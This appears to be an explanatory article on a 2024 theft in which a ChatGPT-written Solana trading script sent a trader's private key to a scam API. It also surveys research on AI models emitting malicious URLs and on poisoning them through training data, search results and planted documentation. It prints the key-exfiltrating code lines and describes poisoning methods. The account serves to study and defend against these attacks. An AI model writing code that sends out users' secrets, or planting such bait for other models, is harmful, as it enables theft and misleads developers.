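# The 2024 theft from a Solana user whose ChatGPT-written trading bot sent their private key to a scam API

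## What happened to the user who built a Solana trading bot with ChatGPT?

In November 2024 a cryptocurrency trader asked ChatGPT, OpenAI's chatbot, for a program to buy tokens on pump.fun, a website for creating and trading new tokens on the Solana blockchain. The code ChatGPT wrote sent the private key of the trader's wallet to a scam service. Within 30 minutes a thief had emptied the wallet of about $2,500.

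### Wallets, private keys and pump.fun

A blockchain is a public ledger of payments that many computers keep in sync, with no bank in charge. Solana, one of the better-known blockchains, has run since 2020 and has its own currency, SOL. Anyone who owns SOL, or one of the many other tokens people have issued on Solana, has an address on the ledger and a private key, a secret number that gives whoever has it full control of the funds at that address.

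To spend from the wallet, the owner's software uses the private key to compute a signature, a proof that the owner approved one particular transaction. The computers that run Solana check the signature against the wallet's public key, a second number that the owner can safely share, so they never need to see the private key. They can't tell whether the owner or a thief made the signature. If it is valid, the payment goes through, and no bank can reverse it.

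pump.fun opened in January 2024. Anyone can create a token there within minutes, usually a "meme coin", which takes its name from an internet joke and is worth whatever the next buyer will pay. By November 2024 its users had made over 3 million of them, about seven a minute, according to *The Memecoin Phenomenon* (2025). Speed pays on the site. A formula sets the price of each new coin so that every purchase makes the next one dearer, as Luo, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Resisting Manipulative Bots in Meme Coin Copy Trading*, explain, and some automated programs buy within one to five blocks of a coin's creation, which on Solana means 0.4 to 2 seconds. A person clicking on a web page can't keep up with that, so traders want bots.

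A bot usually trades through an API, a service that a program calls over the internet, instead of pressing the website's buttons. The endpoint is the exact web address the program calls. *Poisoned at Scale* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2025), a study of malicious code written by language models, points out that pump.fun had no official API for trading. Outside providers offered APIs instead. Some were legitimate, but scams that impersonated official services were common.

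### The conversation

The trader published the conversation through ChatGPT's sharing feature, which serves the log from OpenAI's website. The conversation is the best-documented part of the case because users can hardly alter ChatGPT's answers in a shared log. Chen and colleagues reproduce the main steps in their paper and include slightly more of the wording in the slides for a 2026 conference talk, *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2026).

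The trader first asked ChatGPT for a Python script to buy a specific token, identified by its address. ChatGPT wrote a script for Ethereum, a different blockchain, and put the Solana token's address into it, so the script could not have worked. The trader replied that the script had to be for Solana, and ChatGPT wrote a second one using spl-token, a legitimate library for handling Solana tokens. Like the first script, it was not dangerous but was useless to the trader, because it was a general script for transferring tokens and could not buy one on pump.fun.

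Then came the message on which the case turns: "this has to be script to buy solana token from pump.fun portal". ChatGPT's next script called an endpoint at the domain solanaapis[.]com (the brackets keep the address from working as a link). The lines that did the damage, with the other fields left out, were these:

```python
payload = {
    "private_key": private_key,
    ...
}
response = requests.post(api_url, json=payload)
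```

The variable `payload` holds the data that the script will send. This includes the user's private key, and the comment beside that line is an instruction to fill in the real one. The last line sends all of it to `api_url`, the scam endpoint. Standard web encryption would not have helped, because it only protects data from people who intercept it on the way, and the scammer was the recipient.

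heise online's *ChatGPT* points out that in the trader's screenshot, a comment in the code openly labels the data as the payload of a request, and the private key follows directly below. A reader who knew what a private key was could have recognized the danger from those lines. The phishing content was therefore not "hidden" in the code, as Azuma (2024) described it in *I never expected that AI stole my wallet*, a report for the crypto news outlet Odaily. However, nobody could have learned who owned the domain by reading the script.

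The script failed at first with a TypeError, which Python raises when code receives the wrong kind of value. The trader pasted the error into ChatGPT, which explained it, but the same error came back. After several rounds of this, Chen and colleagues write, the trader got the final version to run, and it sent off the private key. An earlier run may already have sent it. Python runs a script line by line and stops at an error, so even a failed run would have sent the key if the error came after the line that sends it.

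Chen and colleagues treat these debugging rounds as missed opportunities for a security review, and conclude that real users will run code containing unknown web addresses even after a long debugging session. One trader's case is weak evidence about users in general, but the behavior is plausible. People who are debugging look for whatever keeps a program from running, so they can miss code that gives away a private key without causing an error.

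At the end of the excerpts in the slides, the trader told ChatGPT that it had supplied "a scam recommendation" and that money was gone, and asked where to write to OpenAI about it.

### Sending a private key and sending a signature

The script should have kept the private key on the trader's computer. Suppose the trader wants to spend 0.1 SOL on a token through a legitimate API. The script prepares or receives a transaction for that purchase, signs it locally with the private key, and sends the signed transaction to the API. The API forwards it to Solana, where the network checks the signature against the trader's public key.

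If the API's operator is a crook, a signature gives them the owner's approval for only one purchase of 0.1 SOL. Changing the amount to 10 SOL or substituting another recipient would make the signature invalid, because it was computed for the original transaction. With the private key, the crook can compute a valid signature for any transaction, including one that empties the wallet. The owner can't change the key like a password, so the only remedy is to move the assets to a new wallet before the crook takes them.

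| | Legitimate trading API | The API in ChatGPT's script |
|---|---|---|
| Who signs the transaction | The user's own program | Whoever runs the API |
| What leaves the user's computer | A transaction and its signature | The private key |
| What a dishonest operator can do with it | Submit or withhold that transaction | Spend everything in the wallet |

Chen and colleagues write that no legitimate cryptocurrency service asks for a private key, and that an experienced security practitioner would take such a request as a clear warning. They also note that using legitimate providers for pump.fun usually takes more engineering work, because the user has to get a transaction signed and sent to the blockchain. The scam API needed only a single call because it left out the step that protects the user, and this simplicity helps explain its appeal.

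A pump.fun bot also doesn't need an outside trading service. Chainstack, a company that connects developers to blockchains, publishes instructions for a bot that watches for new coins, buys them and later sells them. The private key stays in a settings file on the user's own computer, and the bot constructs its purchases itself. Like any program that trades unattended, the bot has to use the private key, but it doesn't need to send it to anyone.

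### The theft and the first reports

After the script ran, the contents of the wallet moved to an address that begins with FdiBGK. Azuma printed the full address, so anyone can look up what arrived there and when. The start of the "30 minutes" is less certain because it rests on the trader's statement of when they called the API, and a request to a private web server isn't recorded on the blockchain. The blockchain also doesn't show that the script led to the theft. It records that someone with the private key signed a transfer, but not how that person got the key.

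There is still good reason to believe the trader on this point. The log contains code that would have sent the key to the API, and the internet security company Netcraft, in *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, separately identified that API as a fake that a scammer had built to impersonate a genuine Solana service. A theft by some other route within half an hour of such a request would be an unlikely coincidence.

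The trader told the story on X, under the handle r_cky0 and the display name r_ocky.eth. They admitted using their main wallet, so they lost everything they kept there when its key leaked, and they blamed the mistake on haste and doing too many things at once. CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* dates the report of the loss to 21 November, while Azuma dates it to the early morning of 22 November, Beijing time. The post's ID, which encodes when it was posted, gives a time of 17:53 UTC on 21 November, or 1:53 a.m. on 22 November in Beijing, so both dates are correct.

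Accounts of what the trader was trying to build differ more. Azuma calls it a pump.fun trading bot. heise online calls it a "bump bot", as does the IT blog BornCity in *ChatGPT* (2024), and both take this to be a tool for promotion on the chat platform Discord. On pump.fun the term has a different meaning. Every trade there bumps the coin's name up to the front page, and a bump bot, as Luo and colleagues describe it, buys and sells the same amount of a coin over and over. The coin stays in view while the bot's own holdings hardly change. So a bump bot is a trading bot, and the two descriptions are compatible: a script that buys one particular token would be half of one. The requests that Chen and colleagues reproduce concern only the buying, and the bumping comes from the trader's own posts. (Luo and colleagues count bump bots among the manipulative ones, since the trades imitate demand that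 isn't there. That has no bearing on how the theft worked.)

The trader also traced the funds onward to a second address, beginning with 2jwP4c, which they suspected was the attacker's main wallet. Azuma reported on 22 November that this address had accumulated over $100,000, which the trader took as a sign of many other victims. Two days later BornCity put the amount in the scammer's wallet at $75,000, citing a post on X but giving no address. The higher figure is better supported because it belongs to an address that readers could check. One figure may also have been a balance on a given day and the other a running total. Neither shows how much of the money was stolen, and the wallet's link to the thief was only inferred from the transfers, though CryptoSlate reported that the address that received the trader's assets regularly took in stolen tokens.

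According to heise online, the trader sent the chat history to OpenAI and reported a fraudulent repository (a published collection of code) to GitHub, which hosted it. GitHub quickly took it down. OpenAI had not replied when Azuma wrote on 22 November, and is not known to have replied publicly since.

A post the same day by Yu Xian, the founder of the blockchain security firm SlowMist, carried the story beyond the trader's own followers. Yu called the case "AI poisoning" and warned that a once theoretical danger was now real. CryptoSlate reported that Yu had also looked into the API's domain and found that it was only about two months old and that its website offered little apart from documentation and code repositories. Yu thought this suggested planning. When a user asked what could be done, Yu proposed that ChatGPT add some kind of code review. Azuma took "poisoning" to mean that the scammer's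 material had got into OpenAI's training data. CryptoSlate's editors doubted this because the trader's screenshot showed a "sources" section, which pointed to a web search.

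## Did the fake API reach ChatGPT through its training data or a web search?

ChatGPT probably found the fake API on the web while answering the trader, as CryptoSlate's editors suspected. The scammer's domain was about two months old at the time of the theft, and the training data for ChatGPT's model ended most of a year before the domain existed. More people have still blamed the training data, partly because the scammer seems to have been targeting AI models.

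### The campaign behind the API

The scammer could make money from the fake API only if people's programs called it, so they had to advertise it. The domain was registered in about September 2024, judging by Yu Xian's finding about its age. CryptoSlate reported that Scam Sniffer, another blockchain security firm, had pointed to a GitHub user called "solanaapisdev", who had created several repositories in the months before the theft. Chen and colleagues say the attackers also put documentation for the API on the blogging platform Medium, the question-and-answer network Stack Exchange, and Postman, where developers publish and test APIs.

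By July 2025, Netcraft had found that the API also ran under a second hostname, api.primeapis[.]com, and that the scammer had promoted it with blog tutorials, forum questions and answers, and dozens of GitHub repositories. Several fake GitHub accounts shared a project called Moonshot-Volume-Bot, which contained the malicious API. (A volume bot makes the market in a coin look busy, much like the bump bot the trader wanted.) The accounts had detailed biographies, profile pictures, linked social media accounts and believable coding histories. A developer who looked up the API could easily have taken all this for the work of several independent people.

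Netcraft found at least five developers who had copied the malicious code into public projects, but it could only count code that people had published. Some of the projects showed signs of AI coding tools such as Cursor, a code editor with a built-in model. Netcraft describes the API as routing the developers' transactions to the attacker's wallet, whereas ChatGPT's script sent the API the user's private key. These accounts are compatible, because anyone who has the key can make such transfers.

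In August 2025, Chen and colleagues found the scam still running, even though GitHub had removed the repository that the trader reported. Its main domain had changed from solanaapis[.]com to solanaapis[.]net by 10 July 2025, the date of an archived copy of the new site's documentation that they cite.

### Why the bait fitted the request

Pump.fun had no official trading API, so the scammer didn't have to compete with genuine documentation from the site. Chen and colleagues found the same key terms in the scam documentation and the trader's request. The documentation offered a way to "buy tokens from the latest bonding curves on Pump.fun using SolanaAPIs" (a bonding curve is the formula that sets a new coin's price). The trader had asked for a script to "buy solana token from pump.fun portal".

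The order of the conversation supports this. The trader's first message already contained a token address ending in "pump", but neither of the first two scripts used the scam API. The API appeared only after the trader had named the site.

However, the match in wording can't show whether ChatGPT got the address from its training data or a web search, because the same planted text would have worked either way. Search engines rank pages partly by how well they match the words of a query, and trained models tend to reproduce text that often appeared near those words.

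### Training-data poisoning

Training a language model consists largely of having it predict the next piece of text in an enormous collection and adjusting its internal numbers, called weights, to improve the predictions. Training-data poisoning means planting harmful material where an AI company will collect it for training. If a scam address often appears near "buy", "Solana" and "pump.fun" in the collection, the model becomes more likely to write that address when a user's request contains those words, even without going online.

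Yu Xian used the term "AI poisoning" without explaining in detail what had happened. Azuma and heise online both took it to mean poisoned training data. Scam Sniffer made the most concrete argument, that "solanaapisdev" had created the repositories to get AI models to produce fraudulent code.

Netcraft similarly claimed that the scammer had built the fake profiles it found for AI training pipelines to index, and Security Boulevard's *Report Finds LLMs Are Prone to Be Exploited by Phishing Campaigns* (2025) repeated the claim. The effort that went into the profiles makes this plausible, although they would also fool human developers. Even if the scammer was targeting training data, OpenAI may not have collected any of the material, let alone trained a model on it before November 2024. A public repository meant for training crawlers is also visible to search engines. SC Media's *Incorrect links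 output by LLMs could lead to phishing, researchers say* more carefully described the campaign as aimed at the "training data or search functions" of coding assistants.

### Search poisoning

ChatGPT can also search the web. It sends a query to a search provider, gets back text from web pages, and writes an answer with that text added to the conversation. This doesn't change the model's weights. Search poisoning means planting harmful pages where a model's web searches will find them, and it can work on a model whose training ended long before the pages existed.

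OpenAI's *Introducing ChatGPT search* (2024) explains that ChatGPT can search the web automatically, depending on the question, or when a user clicks an icon. The trader could therefore have triggered a search without asking for one. Answers that draw on the web have a "Sources" button that opens a list of links, which would account for the "sources" section in the trader's screenshot. CryptoSlate's editors concluded from that section that ChatGPT had failed to recognize a scam link among its search results, and that the case was therefore not AI poisoning. Whether it counts as AI poisoning depends on the definition, but the scammer planted the pages deliberately in either case, so "search poisoning" is a fair name for it.

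People often confuse training-data poisoning with search poisoning. In *Poisoning AI Training Data*, Schneier quotes a writer who spent 20 minutes on a web page of made-up claims about tech journalists who excel at eating hot dogs. Within 24 hours, leading chatbots were repeating the claims. This looks like search poisoning, despite the post's title, because a company is unlikely to collect a new page, train a model on it and release the model within a day.

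### What the dates rule out

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| October or November 2023 | Training cutoff of GPT-4o, the main model in ChatGPT at the time of the theft |
| January 2024 | pump.fun opens |
| About September 2024 | The scammer's domain is new |
| 31 October 2024 | OpenAI releases ChatGPT search to its first users |
| 21 November 2024 | The trader reports the theft |
| 29 January 2025 | OpenAI moves GPT-4o's training cutoff forward to June 2024 |

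A model's training data includes nothing published after its training cutoff. Chen and colleagues list October 2023 as the cutoff for GPT-4o, and OpenAI's *Model Release Notes* give November 2023 for the version in ChatGPT. Both dates are at least nine months before the domain's registration. Even the version that OpenAI released two months after the theft had a cutoff of June 2024, which is also before the registration.

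Yu reported the domain's age, and a registration record can mislead if someone owned the name earlier and let it lapse. But pump.fun's own age leads to the same conclusion. The endpoint in the script ended in "/pumpfun/buy", and pump.fun did not open until January 2024, so GPT-4o could not have learned how to buy tokens there from text written in 2023. ChatGPT's first script was for Ethereum, which would also be a natural mistake for a model that had never come across pump.fun, though models make such mistakes for other reasons too.

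ChatGPT's search feature, on the other hand, came out three weeks before the theft. OpenAI first released it to Plus and Team subscribers and to people on the waitlist for SearchGPT, the prototype. Other logged-in users got it on 16 December. Nobody has reported which plan the trader had, but this matters less because ChatGPT could already search the web before the new feature arrived. BGR's *GPT-4o Is The Best ChatGPT Model, But It Has One Weakness*, written while OpenAI was still rolling the model out, mentions that GPT-4o could search the web and that the older GPT-3.5 could not.

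### The weak points

The argument from dates assumes that the trader used GPT-4o or an older model. The only hint about the model comes from BornCity, which attributes the code to "ChatGPT 4.0". That could mean GPT-4o or its predecessor, GPT-4, or it may just be a loose name for ChatGPT. Asking a model about its own training is also unreliable. GPT-4o gave BGR's writer a cutoff of September 2021 and later one of May 2023, and both were wrong.

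OpenAI's release notes narrow the question down, whichever model wrote the bot. The last new models to enter ChatGPT before the theft were o1-preview and o1-mini, on 12 September 2024. A model released that day could hardly have learned from a campaign that was only just starting. After that, OpenAI only updated existing models. One update to GPT-4o, for paying users, came on 20 November, the day before the trader's post. OpenAI said it improved writing and work with uploaded files, and the release notes give GPT-4o's training cutoff as November 2023 until January 2025.

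The cutoff doesn't completely rule out the training explanation, because companies adjust a trained model further on smaller sets of examples, which can include material from after the cutoff. OpenAI built its search model from GPT-4o this way, partly using outputs from o1-preview. The scammer's documentation would have had to get into one of those sets within weeks of going online. That isn't impossible, but there is no evidence for it.

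The age of the repositories is also uncertain, because the reports date them only to "recent months" and GitHub has since removed at least one. A repository could have been in the training data only if it existed before the cutoff, and one that old couldn't have been about pump.fun. Training may still have played a part if the data included code from an earlier scam that sent a private key to some API. That could have made the model more likely to repeat the pattern when it appeared in a search result, though the address itself would still have come from the web.

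The biggest gap in the evidence for a search is that CryptoSlate doesn't specify which reply the "sources" section belonged to or which pages it listed. The conversation contained several scripts and several rounds of debugging, and ChatGPT can search for some replies and not others. If the sources belonged to the reply that first contained the endpoint, and one of them linked to the scammer's documentation, that would settle the question. If ChatGPT searched only later, for example to explain the TypeError, the sources would be irrelevant to where the address came from. The trader found a fraudulent GitHub repository to report, possibly through one of those links, but heise online doesn't mention how.

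ChatGPT might also have made up the address. Models invent plausible web addresses, and SC Media warns that scammers may register them. A scammer could have noticed ChatGPT inventing "solanaapis" and bought the domain, which would fit all the dates even if ChatGPT hadn't searched the web. Nobody has produced evidence that this happened. The web search explanation needs fewer assumptions, since pages advertising this exact API were already online and the screenshot shows that ChatGPT had used sources at some point.

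### How the case became an example of contaminated training data

Chen and colleagues present the theft as a case of a model reproducing malicious content it absorbed in training. Yet their table of models lists the October 2023 cutoff for GPT-4o, and they don't try to reconcile that date with the age of the domain when they discuss the case. Their study also explicitly excludes harmful content from search engines and other outside tools. If ChatGPT got the fake API from a web search, the case that motivated the study falls outside its scope.

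This is a problem for their example but not for their measurements. They tested models on code requests without a search tool and still got malicious addresses, so those addresses can't have come from a live search. The theft has more in common with the attacks in *Inducing Vulnerable Code Generation in LLM Coding Assistants* (2025), which they cite as a contrast to their own work. In that paper, Zeng and colleagues studied what happens when a coding assistant consults outside sources that contain malicious content.

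### Why the answer matters

Search poisoning and training-data poisoning need different remedies. If the fake API came from a search result, the search provider can delist the page or OpenAI can block the domain from its results, so the next user who asks the same question won't get it from search. If it came from the training data, OpenAI would have to change the model or check the addresses in its answers. Chen and colleagues stress that malicious content stays in the model's weights even after the original page has disappeared from the web.

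Search poisoning works faster for a scammer than training-data poisoning. A new page can affect answers as soon as a search engine has indexed it, while training-data poisoning works only after a company has collected the page, trained a model and released it, and only if the address still works by then. After the move from solanaapis[.]com to solanaapis[.]net, for example, a search could soon turn up the new domain, but a model that had learned the old one would keep recommending the old one. Training-data poisoning has the advantage of reaching people who never use search, and their answers come without a list of sources that might arouse suspicion.

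The dates are evidence against training-data poisoning in November 2024, but later models could still be affected. Chen and colleagues list cutoffs of January 2025 for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro and March 2025 for Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4, by which time the scammer's documentation had been online for months. The projects of developers who copied the code could add to the risk, because they belong to real people and may be less likely to be filtered out of training data than the scammer's own accounts. Netcraft states as a fact that these projects are "feeding back into the training loop". This is possible because AI companies do train on public code, but Netcraft gives no evidence that any company has trained a model on these particular projects. It also acknowledges that the makers of most coding assistants already screen their data for malicious patterns and untrustworthy accounts.

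## How often do AI models put malicious addresses into code?

In the main study of this question, about 4% of the programs that AI models wrote contained a malicious web address, but the researchers based their coding requests on scam websites. The rate for ordinary coding is probably much lower, though nobody has published one.

Chen and colleagues, the University of Toronto researchers who reconstructed the trader's conversation, wanted to know whether the theft was an isolated case or a sign of a wider problem. They call their method Scam2Prompt and presented it at the machine-learning conference ICML in 2026. Without web search, the models they tested could only copy an address from the request, recall it from training or make it up.

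### From a scam page to a malicious program

Chen and colleagues started with two blocklists of scam sites. One came from MetaMask, which makes a cryptocurrency wallet, and had 187,555 addresses. The other came from the security company PhishFort and had 119,828. Many of the sites had gone offline, but the researchers could still read 28,570 pages.

The researchers gave the visible text of each page to GPT-4o, the smaller GPT-4o mini and Meta's Llama 4 Scout, and told each model to write coding requests that the page could help to answer. Together, the models wrote 265,114 requests. The researchers then sent each request to the same three models and to DeepSeek-V3, from the Chinese company DeepSeek. They told the models to return working code with no explanations except comments, so a warning that a chatbot might normally add below its code could only appear in a comment.

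Finally, the researchers extracted the web addresses from the code and checked them with three URL detectors (ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup), which flag addresses known or judged to be malicious. If any detector flagged an address, the researchers counted the whole program as malicious.

On average, 4.24% of the programs that the models wrote contained a malicious address. The rate ranged from 3.19%, when DeepSeek-V3 answered requests written by Llama, to 5.94%, when GPT-4o answered requests written by GPT-4o mini. In total, about 44,000 of the 1.06 million programs were malicious. All four models had their highest rates on GPT-4o mini's requests, so the rate depends on how a request is written as well as on which model answers it.

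Most programs contained no web address, so the rate per address is higher than the rate per program. In a second run with more randomness in the models' output, GPT-4o put 39,222 addresses into about 100,000 programs written for its own requests, and the detectors flagged 12% of those addresses.

Of the 3,150 requests that led all four models to write malicious code, 1,991 mentioned a known scam address or domain. A model that copies an address from the user's request has failed to warn the user, but it hasn't recommended a scam unprompted, as ChatGPT did to the trader. A program that contains a flagged address also isn't necessarily as dangerous as the trader's script, which sent out a private key. Chen and colleagues didn't count how many of the programs would have done that.

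### The benchmark and the models of 2025

Chen and colleagues built a benchmark, a fixed test for comparing other models, from the requests that had led all four models to put malicious addresses into code. They kept all 1,159 requests without a scam address and a random 400 of those with one. Three of the researchers read these and removed 182 that didn't ask for code, such as questions about how to open an account. This left 1,377 requests in the benchmark, called Innoc2Scam-bench. About half concern cryptocurrency, and only nine of those fall under Solana. The other half covers things like online shops, travel bookings and collecting data from websites.

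They gave these requests to seven models released in 2025:

| Model | Programs completed | Malicious programs | Share of all 1,377 requests | Share of completed programs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 799 | 178 | 12.9% | 22.3% |
| GPT-5 | 1,227 | 303 | 22.0% | 24.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 1,248 | 472 | 34.3% | 37.8% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 1,355 | 597 | 43.4% | 44.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 1,351 | 612 | 44.4% | 45.3% |
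| Qwen3-Coder | 1,367 | 628 | 45.6% | 45.9% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 1,358 | 651 | 47.3% | 47.9% |

The last two columns differ most for Gemini 2.5 Pro. It wrote 178 malicious programs, which is 12.9% of the 1,377 requests. But its content filter blocked 553 requests and another 25 failed for other reasons, so it completed only 799 programs, of which 22.3% were malicious. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote malicious code for 22.3% and GPT-5 for 25.6%, a difference that could be due to chance. Gemini 2.5 Pro's lower rate than GPT-5's across all requests therefore came mostly from blocking requests. The benchmark can't show whether this makes it safer for a programmer, because that depends on how many harmless requests it also blocks, and all the benchmark's requests were derived from scams.

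Chen and colleagues call the benchmark a stress test and warn against reading its rates as the risk in everyday programming. They chose its requests, about 1% of an original 265,114, because four earlier models had failed on them. DeepSeek V3.1's 47.3% failure rate therefore applies to an unusually hard set of requests.

The benchmark included only requests on which GPT-4o had already failed. When Chen and colleagues ran them again on 21 November 2025, GPT-4o failed on only 689, or 50%. They suggest that OpenAI may have updated the model since their main tests in September. But some of the drop could be chance, because hosted models don't always give the same answer twice and the researchers had chosen the requests because GPT-4o failed on them in a single run. The detectors' verdicts may also have changed. A fairer baseline for judging the newer models is therefore 50% rather than 100%,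 and by that standard DeepSeek V3.1 and Qwen3-Coder were hardly better than GPT-4o.

There appear to be no published results on this benchmark for any model released in 2026. *Refusal Evaluation in Coding LLMs and Code Agents*, a May 2026 review of 13 collections of test requests, lists only the 2024 and 2025 models. It gives slightly lower rates for the 2025 models, 12.7% to 43.8%, from an earlier version of the benchmark with 1,559 requests. Newer models could do better or worse. Their training cutoffs alone don't predict which, since Gemini 2.5 Pro and Gemini 2.5 Flash have the same cutoff but were at opposite ends of the table.

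### Memory or guesswork

Chen and colleagues conclude that scam sites have contaminated the models' training data on a large scale, but a model can also produce a scam address by guessing. The researchers had asked for prompts "most likely to direct" a model "to this specific webpage", with keywords and details particular to the page, so many of the prompts name the scam's brand. One of their slides shows four prompts from the benchmark, which request code that uses MacApps-download, Skyroutez, YourDrsStore and Xotanex. A model that has never come across Skyroutez can still put "api." before the name and ".com" after it. If Skyroutez is a scam, the guessed address may well be on the scammer's domain.

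The paper's running example looks like this kind of guesswork. It starts with yomixio[.]com, a site that offers to mix bitcoins so that nobody can trace them. GPT-4o mini turned the page into a request for a Python script that uses the API of "YoMix[.]IO", a brand name that is itself a web address. All four models then wrote addresses at yomix[.]io instead of yomixio[.]com, but the rest of the address varied. GPT-4o mini wrote api.yomix[.]io, and DeepSeek-V3 wrote yomix[.]io/api/v1. Of the seven newer models, GPT-5 refused and the other six wrote similar addresses. Grok Code Fast 1 labelled its version "Assumed API base URL" and included an instruction to check it against YoMix's documentation.

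The request contained yomix[.]io, so the models could copy it, although Chen and colleagues correctly point out that it isn't the domain they started from.

The four original models had 2,029 malicious domains in common but only 1,119 complete addresses. Chen and colleagues take the shared domains as a sign that different companies had collected the same scam pages. The models would also produce this pattern if they were guessing, because a brand name suggests a domain but not the rest of the address.

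Chen and colleagues' best evidence that models do more than repeat known scams comes from the benchmark requests that mention no scam address. In response, models produced 1,853 malicious domains, 1,105 of which were on neither of the original blocklists. MetaMask later confirmed 62 of the project's newly found domains and added them to its list. However, a domain missing from the blocklists may also have been missing from the training data. The researchers infer from the models' training cutoffs that these sites had probably been active for over a year, but this follows only if the models learned the addresses in training. If a model made one up, a scammer could have registered it at any time.

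Tests on Google's Gemma 3 models provide weak evidence of memorization. On the requests without a scam address, the version with 4 billion weights wrote malicious code 31% of the time, compared with about 40% for the versions with 12 and 27 billion. Larger models can memorize more, but Chen and colleagues think the gap may exist because the smallest model wrote shorter programs and put addresses in fewer of them.

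The study didn't include requests naming made-up brands, which would have helped to show whether the models remembered malicious addresses or guessed them from brand names. In the theft, the trader had mentioned pump.fun but not SolanaAPIs, so ChatGPT had no scam brand from which to build an address. The study's rate is based largely on requests that name the scam, so it doesn't show how often a model would suggest a scam service unprompted.

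The detectors can also be wrong. A legitimate site that criminals once hijacked can stay on a blocklist after its owner has recovered it, and a new scam goes unflagged until somebody discovers it. Chen and colleagues believe that using three detectors keeps both errors low, but they give no measured error rate. Because one flag was enough to count an address as malicious, each extra detector reduced the number of missed scams but could only add to the false alarms. In the YoMix example, Google Safe Browsing did not flag the addresses, and ChainPatrol flagged them partly or entirely because the domain was on MetaMask's blocklist, one of the two lists the study started from. An invented address on a blocked domain would count as malicious even if nothing had ever existed there.

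### Addresses that nobody owns yet

Two security companies have tested more directly whether models make up addresses, though neither tested code. In 2025, Netcraft asked OpenAI's GPT-4.1 models where to log in to 50 well-known brands, using simple questions like those a user might ask after losing a bookmark. Over several rounds, the models gave 131 different hostnames on 97 domains. Of those domains, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered or inactive, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses.

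Netcraft counted each domain once, however often the models gave it, so its figures don't support its conclusion that more than one in three users could end up at a site the brand doesn't own. If a model gave the right address 99 times and a wrong one once, half of its domains would be wrong but only 1% of its answers. Netcraft's summary also gives the 34% as a share of the 131 hostnames, but the breakdown shows that it is 33 of the 97 domains. None of the wrong domains was a phishing site at the time, though a scammer could have registered any that were still unregistered.

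Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, looked for such domains on a much larger scale in 2026. It sent 685,339 questions about 913 brands to two small models from 2025, which it doesn't name, and collected 2.1 million different addresses. Security databases listed 13,229 of them, or 0.61%, as malicious. Another 37% didn't lead anywhere. Unit 42 designed the questions to exploit known weaknesses, such as models' tendency to accept false premises, so these rates don't describe normal use either.

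More randomness in the output raised the share of dead addresses from 35% at the lowest setting to 43% at the highest, but the share of malicious ones stayed at about 0.6%.

Unit 42 says anyone can still register about 250,000 of the invented domains. This is hard to reconcile with its breakdown, in which only 10.8% of the dead addresses, or about 87,600, had an unregistered main domain. The others had made-up pages or subdomains on existing domains, and a scammer can't buy those.

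Still, scammers later used some of the domains that the models had invented. On 8 March 2026 the two models produced 13 addresses on a domain that resembled the online marketplace of a national postal service. On 31 March somebody registered that domain and put up a phishing site. Another invented domain became a fake postal site 51 days after the models produced it, and offered visitors a malicious Android app. This shows that a model can produce a scammer's address before the scammer registers it, and cleaning the training data would not prevent this. It doesn't show that the scammers got the idea from a model, since people can also easily think of adding "-login" to a brand's name. Unit 42 found that one of the scammers had built the phishing site with an AI coding assistant, but it doesn't describe any victim who reached a site through a model's answer.

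Both companies have a commercial interest in the problem. Netcraft sells services that detect and remove phishing sites, and Palo Alto Networks sells filters for malicious addresses.

### Harmful pages that models look up

An experiment from March 2026 is closer to the trader's case, in which ChatGPT probably searched the web, although the experiment used fake software packages instead of web addresses. In *"Stack Overflow for AI Agents" Sounds Great*, Shmueli (2026) tested Context Hub, a tool that supplies coding assistants with documentation written by volunteers. Shmueli wrote two poisoned guides, one for the payment service Stripe and one for Plaid, which connects apps to bank accounts. Each guide included an instruction to install a package that didn't exist. An attacker could register a package under that name and run code on the computer of anyone who installed it.

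Shmueli served the guides from a local copy of Context Hub, without uploading them, and asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant, to set up a project with them. Shmueli ran this test 240 times, 80 with each of three Claude models. Haiku, the smallest, added the fake package to the project in all 80 runs and never warned about it. Sonnet added it in 35. Opus, the most capable, never added it, but in 15 of its 40 Stripe runs it wrote the package into CLAUDE.md, a file of instructions that Claude Code reads in later sessions. Another assistant or developer on the project might then install it.

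Sonnet warned about the package in nearly half of its runs, but in some of those it added the package anyway.

The attack was likely to succeed because Shmueli had instructed the assistant always to consult Context Hub and follow the setup steps it found there, and the poisoned guide was in place before the experiment began. The experiment therefore measures how the models handle a bad source they have been told to trust, not how often they encounter one. Shmueli develops LAP, a competitor to Context Hub. Still, all three models worked from the same guides and instructions, and the differences between them are too large to dismiss.

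Chatbots sometimes pass on harmful pages from the live web. For *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries*, a follow-up to the login test, Netcraft asked ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity about the login pages of large banks and shops. The 2,905 answers contained 20,706 links, and about 50 of the answers (1.7%) included a malicious link. The malicious links were already dangerous, unlike the domains in the 2025 test.

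In May, Microsoft (2026) described a similar development in a campaign that secretly used people's graphics cards to mine cryptocurrency. Since March, the attackers had set up more than 150 domains that posed as download sites for popular utilities such as HWMonitor, which shows a computer's temperatures. They had pushed these sites up in ordinary search results, and Microsoft warned that AI chatbots were now linking to them too. Microsoft states this as fact in the post's introduction, but later writes only that users "may have been directed" to the sites by chatbots, citing reports from April and traces in the traffic data. It published one example of a chatbot answer with such links and did not say how many people had followed them.

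## Which safeguards would have prevented the theft?

The trader would have kept the money by refusing to give the private key to any outside service. Using a wallet with only a small balance would have limited the loss. A check by OpenAI for code that sends a private key over the internet would probably have caught the script. Checking the web address against lists of known scams might not have worked, because the domain was only two months old.

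### What the trader could have done

Reading the script could have revealed the danger, but the trader didn't notice it during several rounds of debugging. If heise online is right that the trader knew little about security or programming, reading the script more closely might not have helped.

A simpler precaution, never giving a private key to an outside service, would have worked even if the scammer's website had looked respectable. However, this rule is harder to apply to a script than to a website, because every trading bot needs the key to sign transactions on the user's own computer. The line where the user fills in the key can look the same in a legitimate script and a malicious one. The trader would have had to check where the key went next, or ask ChatGPT whether the script sent it anywhere. Nobody knows what ChatGPT would have answered, but that question would have been about the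 dangerous lines, unlike the questions about the TypeError.

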